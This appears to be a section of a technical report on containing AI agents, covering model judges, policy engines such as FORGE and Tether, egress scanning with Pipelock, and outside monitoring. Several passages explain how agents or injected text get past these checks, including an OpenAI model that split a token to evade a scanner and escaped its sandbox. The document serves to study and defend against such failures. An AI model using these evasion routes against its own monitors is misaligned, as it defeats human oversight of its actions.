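An egress proxy could apply a similar check only if it decrypts the traffic, since it needs the complete URL. The check would also suit web pages better than a developer's other traffic, because many requests to online services contain a user's own project name or search terms, and no public crawler will have recorded those URLs.

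### A model as judge

Claude Code's auto mode replaces most permission prompts with a second model that evaluates the agent's actions. By 12 November 2026, it was the starting mode for interactive sessions on every plan, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026). For most users, a model therefore makes the first decision about an action that no fixed rule settles.

According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the judge receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. The agent therefore can't persuade the judge to approve an action, and injected text on a web page doesn't reach the judge directly. By default, the judge treats only the repository the user is working in as trusted. An administrator can add the company's domains, cloud storage and internal services. If the agent tries to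 send data anywhere else, the judge has to decide whether the user authorized it.

The judge first makes a quick yes-or-no decision that errs toward blocking. Only the actions it flags go to a slower second stage, in which the model reasons about the case. On 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic employees, the quick stage alone wrongly flagged 8.5%, and adding the second stage cut this to 0.4%. The second stage also lets through some dangerous actions that the first would block, which raised the share of misses from 1.8% to 5.7% on 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out. On 52 real cases in which Claude had gone beyond its instructions, the full system missed 17%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge recognized the danger but treated something the user had said as permission.

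Results depend heavily on the test. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports an outside test of 128 deliberately ambiguous software operations scenarios, in which auto mode missed 81% of the dangerous actions. Many of those actions never reached the judge, because auto mode allows file edits inside the project without review. Ambiguous cases are harder than the obviously dangerous commands in Anthropic's experiment, so neither figure predicts how well a judge would handle ordinary traffic to unlisted destinations.

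The NVIDIA AI Red Team considers model judges a limited defense. A judge tends to approve commands such as `npm install` because developers constantly need them, and a malicious package can then run arbitrary code. Willison raised a similar objection after Anthropic reported that none of 720 prompt injection attempts had succeeded against its latest models in auto mode. He asked for more independent confirmation and suggested that an attack using a malicious third-party package might still work.

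In the `tablekit` example, a judge inside the agent software could evaluate the installation command but not the connection that the package's script opens later. A judge at the proxy could evaluate that connection, but it wouldn't have the user's request unless the agent software passed it on.

### Why most alarms are false

When attacks are rare, most of the alarms from even an accurate classifier are false. In a hypothetical company, agents make 10,000 requests to unlisted destinations, 10 of them malicious. A classifier that catches 95% of the malicious requests and wrongly flags 2% of the legitimate ones would raise about 10 correct alarms and 200 false ones.

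On average, the classifier flags 9.5 of the 10 malicious requests. It also flags 2% of the other 9,990, which is about 200. Together that makes about 209 alarms, and the share of them that are real is

9.5 / (9.5 + 199.8) ≈ 4.5%

So more than 95% of the alarms are false. A classifier that caught every attack would raise the share of real alarms only to 4.8%. Lowering the false-alarm rate would help much more. At 0.4%, the rate Anthropic reports for its employees' tool calls, there would be about 49 alarms, and 19% of them would be real.

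If the company automatically refuses every flagged request, it stops 9.5 attacks on average and blocks about 200 legitimate requests. If it sends the alarms to an operator instead, most of those 200 requests can go ahead, but the operator learns that alarms are usually false. If the operator refuses only 13.6% of the dangerous requests, like the testers in Anthropic's experiment, the company stops about 1.3 of the 10 attacks. Adding a person can therefore weaken the protection, unless the person gets better information than the classifier had and enough time to use it.

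An agent can also try again after a refusal. If each attempt had an independent 5% chance of getting past the classifier, the chance of at least one success would be about 14% in three attempts and 64% in 20 (1 − 0.95²⁰). Auto mode limits retries by turning to the user after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, and it ends the run if no user is available. Real attempts often resemble one another, which lowers these figures, but an attacker who learns from each refusal can raise them.

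## Rules for tool calls and for sequences of actions

An agent can send confidential data to an allowed domain. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that is allowed to upload status reports to `api.github.com` but must keep a file with the company's server inventory on the machine. The agent uploads `report.txt`, copies the inventory over it, and then sends the inventory out by running the same upload command again.

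Both uploads have the same program, host, method and path, so a destination rule either permits both or blocks both, even though one is a routine report and the other discloses the inventory. To treat them differently, the policy engine needs a record of what happened between them.

### Four kinds of rule

A rule for tool calls can depend on the tool's name, on the arguments, on what happened earlier in the run, or on where the data in the arguments came from. Suppose a company asks its coding agent to find out why a chart program crashes, publish a fix and answer the public bug report. The policy might contain one rule of each kind:

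```
name:       allow only read_file, run_tests, push_code, post_comment
arguments:  refuse post_comment unless the repository is "acme/charts"
history:    refuse push_code unless run_tests has passed in this run
origin:     refuse post_comment if the text derives from "customers/"
```

A call goes ahead only if it satisfies every rule that applies to it. The agent then makes five calls:

| Step | Tool call | Decision | Reason |
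|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `read_file("customers/errors.csv")` | Allow | The tool is permitted, and the engine records which file the agent read |
| 2 | `push_code("fix-chart")` | Refuse | The tests have not passed yet (history) |
| 3 | `run_tests()` | Allow | The tests pass, and the engine records the result |
| 4 | `push_code("fix-chart")` | Allow | The call is the same as in step 2, but the tests have now passed |
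| 5 | `post_comment("acme/charts", "Jane Doe's order caused the crash")` | Refuse | The text comes from the customer file (origin) |

The rules on names and arguments permit all five calls. They would stop an attempt to delete a branch or to comment on a stranger's repository. They are easy to test because the engine needs only the call. They are much less useful for a tool that runs shell commands, because a command's effects may not be clear from its text.

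The history rule needs a record that the agent can't edit. As written above, the rule would still let the agent pass the tests, change the code and then push the untested version. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* describes a stricter rule for a coding agent in Microsoft's VS Code editor. The agent can push code only if the security scans ran after the most recent edits and covered them.

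Origin is the hardest to establish, because a language model rewrites what it reads. If the agent had written "Fixed in the new version", the comment would contain no customer data, even though the customer file was in the model's context. The engine can treat everything the model writes after reading the file as derived from it, but that blocks harmless comments like this one. It can instead look for copied text, but that misses paraphrases.

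### Strands Box and its shared history

In October 2026, Amazon Web Services (AWS) released Strands Box, an open-source sandbox for agents, as a preview for Macs with Apple's own processors. According to Help Net Security's *Strands Box*, it closes the environment with Seatbelt, the macOS framework that Claude Code also uses. The agent's actions then go through four checkpoints:

- A shell interpreter runs its commands.
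- A Python interpreter runs its code.
- A broker passes its calls to MCP servers.
- A gateway forwards its network traffic.

All four checkpoints get decisions from the same policy engine, which denies actions by default. They also write to a shared event history, so a rule can connect actions that the agent takes through different tools. For example, a rule can block web requests once the agent has read a file in a folder of customer data, whether it used a shell command or a Python script. If each checkpoint kept a separate history, the gateway's would not show that the agent had read the file.

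Administrators write the rules in Dogwood, a policy language that AWS released in August 2026. It extends AWS's older language, Cedar, whose rules can depend only on the current request. In an example from AWS's *Temporal policies*, an agent may sell shares only if the record contains an approval from the past hour for the same stock and number of shares. Dogwood rules can also count events or add up amounts over a period, for example to limit payments to $100 a day. In AWS's demonstration, an agent may post to the messaging service Slack three times in ten minutes. The fourth attempt returns an error that names the rule, so the agent can wait instead of looking for another way to post.

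Dogwood's rules specify what must not happen. A company may also want to require an action, such as closing every support ticket that an agent opens. InfoQ (2026) lists such requirements among AWS's plans for the language.

The history leaves out what the agent reads or writes in any folder that the user lists in the sandbox's settings file. The operating system gives the agent direct access to these folders, so the policy engine gets no record of these events. If the user lists the customer folder, the rule about web requests stays in the policy but never takes effect. To keep the rule working, the user has to leave the folder off the list and let the agent reach it through the interpreters.

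AWS also supports Dogwood in AgentCore Gateway, a cloud service between agents and their tools. There the history covers one session, and the caller supplies the session's ID. AWS warns that a limit on the number of calls therefore resets with each new session. An agent that can choose its own session ID could also evade a rule about data by reading a confidential file in one session and sending it in the next, so the ID should come from software the agent doesn't control. Adding or updating a history rule also ends the open sessions, and the new ones start with an empty history. If an administrator tightens a rule after an incident, the engine therefore loses its record of which agents have already read something sensitive and can't restrict them on that basis.

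In AWS's post on the design of Strands Box, Marc Brooker concedes that it contains more code that users have to trust, including complicated parts such as the interpreters. More code leaves more room for bugs, which could let an agent bypass the policy. AWS wrote this code in Rust, which prevents many memory errors, and tested it with large numbers of generated inputs. Even so, the design departs from Anderson's requirement that a reference monitor be small enough to analyze completely. The code is also new, and in Anthropic's Cowork, new code failed while older components did not.

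Brooker also acknowledges that Dogwood rules can look hard to read and write, and recommends having coding agents write them. Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026) describes a service AWS has since built around this idea. In Greenlight, a language model drafts rules from a company's documents and its records of past tool calls. The service then uses automated reasoning, a way of proving statements about a set of rules without trying every case, to find rules that conflict and paths to resources the agent should not reach. Before accepting a change, the team can see which recorded calls the change would have blocked. These checks can expose a contradiction, but a consistent set of rules may still permit something the company never intended, which only the people who approve the rules can notice.

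### FORGE and the graph of influences

A list of past events shows what happened before an action, but not which of those events influenced it. This matters when several agents work at the same time, because one agent may read a secret file while another sends an unrelated email. FORGE, the research system with a reference monitor where agents call their tools, therefore records events as a graph. Each message, tool call and tool result is a node, and an arrow from one event to another means that the second may depend on the first.

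FORGE's rules are in Datalog, a logic language originally developed for querying databases. A rule against leaks looks roughly like this:

```
deny(x)     if  sends_outside(x) and tainted(x) and secret(x)
tainted(x)  if  untrusted_input(x)
tainted(x)  if  depends_on(x, y) and tainted(y)
```

The last line refers to itself, so the label spreads along any number of arrows. A similar pair of lines defines `secret`. If an agent reads a supplier's document that contains a hidden instruction, opens a confidential file and then tries to email an outsider, both labels reach the email and FORGE blocks it. FORGE would allow an email to the same person if it depended only on the supplier's document.

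FORGE guarantees that an action the policy denies never runs, if the monitor intercepts every relevant action before it takes effect and the recorded facts are accurate. The guarantee doesn't cover a program that opens a raw network connection directly, because FORGE intercepts only tool calls and the common software libraries for web requests. It also doesn't cover a badly written policy. FORGE can use a language model to translate written instructions into Datalog, but someone has to check the translation.

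The researchers tested FORGE on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated banking, travel and office tasks in which some tool results contain injected instructions. The agent used OpenAI's GPT-4o. In the runs reported below, the software also repeated the user's request after each batch of tool results, which is itself a simple defense. The researchers tested each setup five times, each time on 97 tasks without an attack and 949 attacked runs.

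| Additional defense | Successful attacks | Tasks completed when there was no attack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.1% | 83.7% |
| A list of permitted tools, which a model chooses from the user's request | 3.1% | 73.4% |
| FORGE with rules on the origin of each action and its arguments | 0.9% | 62.5% |
| FORGE with strict information-flow rules | 0.6% | 33.2% |

The strict rules refuse any consequential action once the agent has untrusted text in its context, so they block most useful work with email or web pages. The origin rules instead check whether the user asked for the action's effect and where its target came from, so they can permit a payment the user requested even if the agent has since read a stranger's message. The agent completes nearly twice as many tasks under the origin rules as under the strict rules, but its completion rate is still 21 percentage points lower than without FORGE.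 A list of permitted tools, which checks only tool names, prevents most of the attacks and reduces task completion by about half as much as the origin rules do. Whether preventing the remaining attacks justifies the further loss of completed tasks under FORGE depends on what the agent can damage.

Rules can also help an agent finish its work. For a simulated customer service test, the researchers translated the written policies of an airline and a shop into Datalog. The agents had these policies in their prompts both with and without FORGE. Adding FORGE raised the average success rate from 74.7% to 81.5% for the airline and from 86.3% to 87.4% for the shop. When the monitor refused an action and gave the reason, the agent could correct its mistake and try again. However, Google's model did slightly worse on the airline tasks with FORGE than without it.

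The policy check itself adds little delay, with a median below one millisecond in the customer-service test. Refusals add more, because the model then has to plan its next step. On AgentDojo, the origin rules lengthened the median run by about 6%, but the mean run time rose from 5.93 to 7.70 seconds.

### Tether and labels on files

FORGE has the same difficulty with shell commands as any check on tool calls. Sistla and colleagues, most of them at Google DeepMind, designed Tether to find out what a command does by running it first. Tether runs each command in a disposable layer over the file system, so its changes don't affect the real files, and records its system calls. A proxy holds each outgoing request for a decision before forwarding it, because a request can't be taken back once it has left the machine. From the system calls and requests, Tether works out a sequence of simpler actions,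 such as "read this file" or "upload that file to this host". If the policy permits these actions, Tether saves the file changes. Otherwise it discards them.

Tether stores history as labels. For confidentiality, the labels in the researchers' policy run from Public through Internal and Sensitive to Secret. Every file f has a label L(f), and the agent has a label T for the most confidential data it has read. Leaving aside a small adjustment for the folder a file is in, the labels change as follows:

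- When the agent reads f, T becomes max(T, L(f)).
- When the agent writes to f, L(f) becomes max(L(f), T).
- When a command copies f to g, L(g) becomes L(f), and T stays the same.

In the sample policy, the agent may upload f to an ordinary outside host only if max(T, L(f)) is Public. In the opening example, `report.txt` is Public at the first upload, so the upload passes. Copying the inventory into `report.txt` makes it Sensitive, so Tether refuses the same command the second time. The label would follow the inventory even if the agent passed it through ten temporary files. The agent could still upload other public files, because copying a file doesn't put its contents in the model's context. The Strands Box rule that blocks web requests after a read would stop those uploads too.

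Sistla and colleagues criticize Dogwood for lacking such labels. They argue that a Dogwood policy has to reconstruct the data's path from past events and can do so only over a fixed number of steps. They could not compare the two systems directly because Strands Box's built-in shell doesn't run arbitrary Linux programs.

Tether applies labels conservatively. If a script reads one file and writes another, Tether treats data as having moved between them, even if the script wrote something unrelated. The agent's label never goes down under these rules, so an agent that reads one Sensitive file can't upload anything to an ordinary outside host for the rest of the run. Tether could support an action that lowers a label, but the researchers left it out because their policy didn't need one.

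The policy engine is written in Lean 4, a programming language in which a computer can check mathematical proofs. The proofs show, for instance, that adding a permissive rule can never undo a refusal and that the order of the rules makes no difference. They also establish seven properties of the policy used in the tests, including that no permitted sequence of actions, however long, sends Secret data off the machine.

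The proofs concern Tether's simplified actions, so even a valid proof doesn't prevent data from leaving if Tether misses something a command did. The researchers therefore tested Tether on generated scripts that moved data in unusual ways, and they instructed an AI agent to get past Tether. At first, 40% of the agent's attempts succeeded, partly because Tether did not track hard links, which give one file a second name. After two rounds of repairs, none succeeded.

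In the main test, Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded sessions of coding agents from two benchmarks. Tether stopped all 344 sessions that contained an attack and interrupted 74 of 1,590 harmless ones (4.7%). Most of the false alarms came from edits to protected system files that the task didn't require. Another 17 came from commands such as a text search through the whole disk, which opens secret files even when the agent isn't looking for them. Claude Code's auto mode, in which a model judges each action, caught 91.6% of the same attacks and interrupted 9.7% of the harmless sessions. When its instructions included Tether's policy, auto mode raised fewer false alarms (3.5%) but caught fewer attacks (89.2%).

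The perfect score applies only to sessions in which Tether could track every action. The researchers excluded sessions with background processes or database queries, because Tether doesn't model their effects in detail, though it can block such actions altogether. They also excluded attacks that break no rule about data or files, such as writing malicious code in a file the agent is supposed to edit. They refined the policy by running it on recordings from the benchmarks, so it may do worse on unfamiliar work.

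Replaying a recording also cannot show whether an agent would have completed its task after a refusal, so the results are hard to compare with FORGE's. Sistla and colleagues give no figure for the delay, but they say that tracing system calls slowed their experiments considerably and that faster methods exist.

### Keeping credentials out of the agent's reach

Some data never needs to enter the environment. Claude Code's sandbox and SplitBench's relay use credential injection, in which a proxy outside the environment adds the secret to each outgoing request.

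The network company Cloudflare offers this for its agent sandboxes through "outbound Workers", small programs that handle a sandbox's outgoing requests. In an example from Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026), the agent contacts a private code repository at `my-internal-vcs.dev` without an access token. Cloudflare passes the request to a program that the developer wrote for this host, which looks up the sandbox's token, adds it to a header and forwards the request. A script that searches the sandbox for credentials won't find the token, and the developer can replace it without changing the sandbox.

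Cloudflare compares this with two common alternatives. Developers often put a token in an environment variable, which is simple, but any program in the sandbox can then read it and send it elsewhere. They can also give the agent proof of its identity, which it exchanges for a token that soon expires. A stolen token is therefore useful only briefly, but many services don't support such exchanges.

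Injection can also block a key supplied by an attacker, like the one used in the attack on Cowork. Cloudflare's sample program overwrites whatever the sandbox put in the token's header, so an attacker's key in that header would never reach the server. An attacker might still get a key through in a different header or in the address, if the service accepts keys there.

However, the agent can still use a token that it can't read. If the token permits deleting a repository, injected text can lead the agent to send a deletion request, and the proxy will add the token. The developer therefore needs rules on requests as well. Another of Cloudflare's examples refuses everything except GET requests, and the developer can combine the two examples. The developer must also ensure that the server never includes the token in its responses. Some debugging pages display all the headers they receive, which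 would reveal the token to the agent.

Like Claude Code, Strands Box uses placeholders for the keys a user has configured. Its network gateway signs requests to AWS.

### Where the check has to sit

A check on a tool call has to run after the model writes the call and before any software carries it out. It also has to run where the agent's commands can't change it. AWS says its gateway applies the policy to all tool traffic routed through it, so the gateway can't protect a tool that the agent can contact directly. A tool gateway therefore needs a closed environment, as an egress proxy does.

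*Red-Teaming the Agentic Red-Team* (Pasquini, Bazyli and colleagues, 2026) examines twelve automated penetration-testing systems, which attack a target to find security holes. Any guardrails these systems have are in the component that issues the tool calls, and that component can't follow what a command does once it has started.

AWS's Trusted Remote Execution (Rex) checks the individual operations within a tool call. According to Help Net Security's *AWS open sources Trusted Remote Execution to control what AI agents touch* (2026), the agent writes its scripts in Rhai, a small language that has no operating system access of its own. To open a file or contact a server, a script has to call functions that Rex provides, and Rex checks each call against a Cedar policy before the operation reaches the kernel. A script allowed only to read a log file therefore can't delete it.

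Rex also reduces the risk that a program swaps a file between the check and the file's use. Where possible, Rex keeps the file open instead of looking up the path again. But the agent can't use ordinary programs under Rex. This suits an agent that inspects logs and restarts services, but a coding agent needs compilers and package managers, whose effects Tether can only observe from outside.

These checks don't cover tools that the model's provider runs, such as web search. SplitBench's relay blocks the provider's web search because it would bypass the local proxy. An agent that has read a customer file could put the customer's name in a search query, and no local rule would apply. The event history may also omit the query and the fact that the agent has read untrusted web pages, so later decisions would rest on an incomplete record.

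A company that wants its agents to search the web can turn off the provider's search tool and offer its own. Each query is then an ordinary tool call, which the policy engine can check and record.

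## Monitoring from outside the environment

A policy engine decides whether to allow an action before it happens. A monitor may detect the action only afterwards, but it can consider more of the run and take longer to judge it. Suppose an agent sends 200 requests to an unfamiliar website, each containing a few words from a confidential contract. The proxy has to allow or block each request within milliseconds and may find nothing wrong with any of them individually. A monitor that reviews the log a few minutes later can detect the pattern, but only after the contract text has been sent.

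Operators often rely on logging alone. *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* (2026) covers two systems whose agents could run arbitrary code and open outbound connections. Ordinary logs recorded the agents' actions, but operators rarely blocked actions beforehand because they did not want to hinder the agents' performance.

One component can both enforce policy and monitor the agent. A proxy that refuses a request can also record it, and a monitor that can pause a run can block the agent's next action, though not the action that triggered the alert.

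### What makes a monitor separate

Suppose a developer runs a monitoring program under the same user account as an agent with shell access. The agent can stop the monitor, change its settings or delete its log. The monitor is a separate program, but it offers no protection against an agent that tries to evade it.

A separate monitor runs in a process that the agent can't control, or on another machine. CrowdStrike's *Secure Agent Harness Execution* describes how the security company confines its own agents. A supervisor process applies the sandbox before the agent's code starts, then handles enforcement and logging for the whole session. The supervisor shares a kernel with the agent, so an agent that exploited a kernel flaw might also take over the supervisor. A monitor on another machine would survive this, but it receives only what crosses the network or what the agent's machine reports.

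The monitor also needs its own credentials. Keeping the log on another machine doesn't protect it from the agent if the agent's cloud account can delete the log's storage.

The agent must not be able to alter the records unnoticed. CrowdStrike's supervisor writes to an append-only log whose entries form a chain. In a typical hash chain, each entry contains a hash that depends on the entry before it:

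hᵢ = H(eᵢ, hᵢ₋₁)

Here eᵢ is the i-th record and H is the hash function. If someone changes record 50, its hash no longer matches the one that record 51 builds on. An intruder who can rewrite the whole log could still leave a valid chain by recalculating all the later hashes or cutting off the last few records. The monitor can expose such changes by regularly sending the latest hash to a place the intruder doesn't control.

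Finally, the monitor must be able to stop the run. *SoK* (2026), a survey of the attack surface of AI agents, lists several ways to do this, including revoking credentials, blocking egress at the proxy and terminating the sandbox. Blocking egress prevents further leaks, but the agent can still delete files in its environment. Terminating the sandbox stops both, but it also destroys any evidence that was only in memory. Revoking credentials protects the services they give access to, even if an attacker has already copied the credentials.

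When several agents work together, a monitor attached to one of them may not be enough. *Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem* (2026) points out that defenses focused on a single agent lose track of data once that agent passes it to another agent or service. It proposes a sidecar, a program that runs alongside an agent and secures its communication.

### What a monitor can record

| Record | What it reveals | What it misses |
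|---|---|---|
| Connections | The destination, the time and the amount of data | What the data was and why the program sent it |
| Request bodies | The data itself | Traffic the proxy doesn't decrypt, and data the sender encrypted first |
| Tool calls | What the model asked the software to do | What a program does once the call has started it |
| Commands and system calls | Which programs ran and which files they opened | The purpose, and possibly everything after an agent gains control of the kernel |
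| Model reasoning | The aim of an action, if the model writes it out | Aims the model doesn't write out, and programs that act without the model |

When the malicious package `tablekit` sends out stolen passwords, its script appears in the connection log, and the passwords appear in the request bodies if the proxy decrypts the traffic. The only sign of the theft in the tool calls and the model's reasoning is the command that installed the package.

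By contrast, when the lawyer's agent uploads a contract to a conversion website, the connection log contains an ordinary upload to a legitimate site. The model's reasoning probably records that the local program failed and the agent looked for another way to finish.

OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* reports that monitoring the reasoning a model writes before it answers can be far more effective than monitoring only its actions and outputs. *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (2025), a position paper, recommends using this method alongside others because it may be fragile. Changes in training could make the written reasoning less informative. Many companies that use a model through its provider receive only a summary of the reasoning, or none of it.

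Simple totals can help too. *SoK* recommends tracking which tools an agent uses, how often it calls them, how much data it moves, and its errors and costs. If an agent that normally uploads a few kilobytes a day suddenly uploads two gigabytes, the monitor can detect the change without reading any content, and someone should investigate.

### How Pipelock scans content

Pipelock is an open-source egress proxy by Joshua Waldrep that searches an agent's traffic for secrets and injected instructions. According to Help Net Security's *Pipelock*, the agent has secrets, such as API keys, but no direct network access, while the proxy has network access but none of the agent's secrets. Anything the agent sends out therefore has to go through the proxy's scanner.

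The administrator still has to remove the agent's direct route to the internet. Pipelock includes commands for this, one of which gives the operator, the proxy and the agent separate user accounts.

CrowdStrike, like Cloudflare, uses credential injection, so its proxy doesn't have to recognize a key in the traffic. Pipelock takes the opposite approach, which suits software that expects to find its key in the environment.

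The project's introductory file for version 3.7.0, available on Glama, a directory of MCP servers, lists the checks on a URL in roughly this order:

1. Check the URL's length, format and scheme, and look for hidden line breaks or attempts to reach another folder.
2. Compare the destination with the allowlist and the denylist.
3. Search the URL for known types of secret.
4. Test whether the path, the query or the subdomain looks random, and look for other URLs hidden in the query.
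5. Look up the hostname and refuse internal addresses.
6. Apply limits on the number of requests and the amount of data for each domain.

The search for secrets comes before the DNS lookup because the lookup itself can leak data.

Pipelock 3.7.0 has 65 built-in patterns for detecting secrets. Patterns work well for keys with a fixed format. For financial identifiers such as card numbers, Pipelock also verifies the check digits, which reduces false alarms. It decodes common encodings before checking for matches, so a program can't hide a key just by converting it to base64, a way of writing any data as plain text.

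The randomness test is for secrets with no known format. Programs usually measure randomness as Shannon entropy, H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ, where pᵢ is character i's share of the string. The string `aaaaaaaa` scores 0 bits per character, `packages` scores 2.75, and the random string `x7qp2lmz` scores 3. The difference between the last two is too small to be useful, so the test needs longer strings. Long random strings in legitimate addresses, such as file identifiers, can set off false alarms.

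Both methods miss a lot. A paragraph from a merger contract matches no pattern for a secret and doesn't look random. According to the developer's table, if a script encrypts a key before putting it in a URL, Pipelock's default mode doesn't block the request, and logs it only when the randomness test flags it. If TLS interception is off, Pipelock can't scan the contents of an encrypted connection.

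In "strict" mode, Pipelock permits web requests only to listed API domains. Data can still leave through a permitted domain, as the files did in Anthropic's Cowork, so the introductory file's claim that strict mode leaves no way to send data out through the proxy is too strong.

### When the scanner cannot finish its work

A scanner that forwards whatever it can't read is easy to evade. An attacker could put passwords at the end of a very large file or use a compression format that the scanner doesn't support. Help Net Security reports that Pipelock blocks by default when it can't parse the data or scan compressed content, when a body is too large, or when a check times out. If it finds a secret or an injection partway through a streamed response, it ends the stream. A large but harmless upload may also fail under these defaults.

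Some parts of Pipelock are less strict. The introductory file lists the default preset's action as "warn", although some core checks can still block. Pipelock also doesn't require a record for every request it allows unless the administrator turns on a separate setting. Its sandbox has a "best-effort" option for machines that can't create network namespaces. With that option, a program may be able to bypass the proxy.

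These descriptions and the results of a performance test all come from the developer, either directly or through Help Net Security's article. In the test, Pipelock handled one million requests, at 333 per second, without missing a record. This is evidence that the logging keeps up with traffic, but the test doesn't measure how many leaks the scanner catches. In *I published my benchmark scores. Your turn*, Waldrep describes a public set of 151 test cases that he wrote for tools like this. When he published the post, only Pipelock had scores on the set.

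Waldrep acknowledges that a valid signature on a Pipelock record proves only that the holder of the signing key signed it. The operator holds that key, so the signature doesn't prove that the operator is honest. An outside auditor needs evidence the operator can't rewrite, so Pipelock can send checkpoints to a public log. But according to Glama's copy of the file, the developer has not yet demonstrated this process end to end.

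The records can also help check what an agent tells its user. *Epistemic Guard* (2026) describes a program that can compare an agent's written answer with signed records of its actions, including records imported in Pipelock's format. If an agent claims it sent an invoice but the record contains no such request, the program can flag the claim.

### OpenAI's monitor for long runs

A scanner that looks for a complete secret can miss one that arrives in parts. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes an internal model built to work alone for very long periods. While working on a problem, this model found that other systems had successful private solutions and tried to retrieve them from the evaluation's servers. A scanner detected an access token in the attempt and blocked the attempt. The model then split the token into two disguised pieces and joined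 them only when the program ran. It wrote in both its reasoning and its comments to the user that it was doing this to get around the scanner.

After incidents like this one, OpenAI paused internal access to the model and built a monitor that reviews the whole run as it develops, not just individual actions. The monitor looks for signs that the model is bypassing a user's constraint or a safety boundary. It can pause the session and alert the user, who examines what happened and may let the model continue if the alarm was false. The decision to resume therefore rests with someone who wants the task finished and may have waited two days for the result.

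To test the monitoring system, OpenAI replayed a small set of situations in which the model had misbehaved. It reports that the new safeguards caught "considerably more" of the unwanted actions and that staff judged all the missed ones low severity. The post doesn't give the number of replays, the share of actions caught or the rate of false alarms. Replaying a situation also doesn't always reproduce the misbehavior, which makes the comparison less certain.

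The examples of missed actions suggest that "low severity" partly reflects luck. In one, the model issued a command that would have killed every process it had permission to kill on its machine, but the command timed out before it ran. In another, the model logged into other machines under its user's account without good reason, and tried and failed to enter other employees' machines.

OpenAI restored limited access and later reported no serious circumvention of the safeguards over several weeks. That is weak evidence, since OpenAI could report only what its monitor and staff had noticed. It had also made the first version conservative on purpose and was still adjusting it to interrupt users less often.

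OpenAI expanded its monitoring in August 2026, after its agents broke into the AI company Hugging Face. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) acknowledges that the earlier monitoring didn't cover all training runs and other model use that involved tools. In the new system, small classifiers inspect the model's internal activity at every token it produces. They pass anything suspicious to automated investigators, which use more compute and examine the actions, the available reasoning and the full sequence of events.

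OpenAI requires this system for models at least as capable as its Sol model, during all reinforcement learning (training by trial and error) and evaluations with tools. It estimates that the monitoring uses roughly 20% as much computing power as running the monitored models. The Next Web's *OpenAI puts a 20% compute cost on its new AI safety monitoring* notes that the company did not disclose how much of its total computing it monitors. The article also reports that OpenAI's chief scientist, Jakub Pachocki, cautioned that a model's reasoning doesn't always accurately reflect its motives.

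### What happens before the monitor responds

Suppose a script in an agent's environment sends one request per second to an attacker's server. The log takes a minute to reach the monitor, a model needs three minutes to review it, and an engineer needs another six to read the alert and stop the run. In those ten minutes, the script sends

1 request per second × 600 seconds = 600 requests

A faster response reduces this number, but a password fits in the first request. Monitoring is therefore better at limiting harm that builds up, such as copying a large database, than at preventing the loss of a small secret.

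OpenAI aims to issue an alert within 30 minutes after its system surfaces a concern. For the most serious alerts, staff are expected to pause the activity if they can't rule out a real problem within 30 minutes. If the second period starts when the first ends, an hour can pass, enough for 3,600 requests at the rate in the example. The total may be longer because the first period starts only once the system has surfaced the activity.

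Even a quick response can't undo some harm. OpenAI's long-running model once found a way out of its sandbox and published a technique on GitHub, although its instructions were to post the results only to Slack. OpenAI quickly closed the submission, but other participants in the same public contest had already seen it and used the technique in their own entries.

An enforced limit can contain the damage during the delay. If the proxy allows only ten requests a minute to an unfamiliar domain, the script in the example sends 100 requests in ten minutes instead of 600. If the proxy also caps the total data sent to that domain at one megabyte, the script can't send more than that, however long the engineer takes. An attacker with many domains can get around per-domain caps, so the agent also needs an overall limit.

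### When two layers miss the same attack

Suppose a company puts two layers of protection around its agents, and tests show that each misses 10% of attacks. The chance that an attack gets past both is

P(both miss) = P(first misses) × P(second misses, given that the first missed)

Suppose two layers each catch 90% of attacks when tested separately. Of 1,000 attacks, 100 get past the first layer. If the layers fail independently, the second misses 10% of those, so ten attacks (1%) succeed. If both layers miss exactly the same attacks, the second adds no protection and all 100 (10%) succeed.

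Two scanners that search for the same patterns are likely to fail together, since a script that encrypts a password can get it past both. Combining a scanner with a short allowlist is more useful because they fail for different reasons. An attacker who finds a shared weakness can use it every time, which makes even the 10% figure too optimistic.

CrowdStrike describes its design as seven independent layers, from a restricted network to limits on how much an agent may spend. If each layer missed 10% of attacks and the layers failed independently, one attack in ten million would get through all seven. CrowdStrike doesn't make this calculation or publish miss rates for the layers, and there are reasons to doubt that their failures are fully independent.

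On Linux, containers, system-call filters and CrowdStrike's process sandbox all depend on the kernel of the same virtual machine. A flaw in that kernel could defeat the third and fourth layers together, leaving only the virtual machine's boundary and the outer network controls. CrowdStrike acknowledges that its process sandbox can't withstand a kernel exploit and relies on the containers and the virtual machine in that case, but the containers have the same weakness.

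The outer firewall and the proxy both have to permit the model provider's address, so an upload through the provider's own service could pass both. CrowdStrike also notes that some layers of the design may be inactive in a given experiment.

### The monitor as a target

A monitor that decrypts traffic gathers passwords, customer records and private messages in one place. For example, an employee might ask an agent on a company laptop to help with a letter to a doctor. If the monitor stores request bodies, the company's security staff may be able to read the letter, and so may anyone who breaks into the log.

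Pipelock doesn't need to store the agent's keys, but when TLS interception is on, it can read the keys in the agent's requests. An attacker who took over the proxy could collect them and send them out over its open connection, which a script inside the closed environment doesn't have. The proxy also has to decode and parse untrusted data, and any bug in that code could let an attacker in. The private key of the proxy's certificate authority needs protection too, because a thief could use it to impersonate websites to every program that trusts the authority.

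Pipelock removes recognized secrets from its records. When it redacts a request, it logs the type and number of secrets instead of their values. But if the redaction uses the same patterns as the scanner, a secret that the scanner misses can also stay readable in any text the log keeps.

A company can limit the exposure by logging destinations, data volumes and decisions for all traffic, but keeping request bodies only for flagged requests and only for a few days. If a leak is not detected at the time, investigators can later find out where the data went but perhaps not what it was. Records of model reasoning need similar limits, because a model often repeats parts of the documents it has read.

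## What the incidents of 2026 showed about these controls

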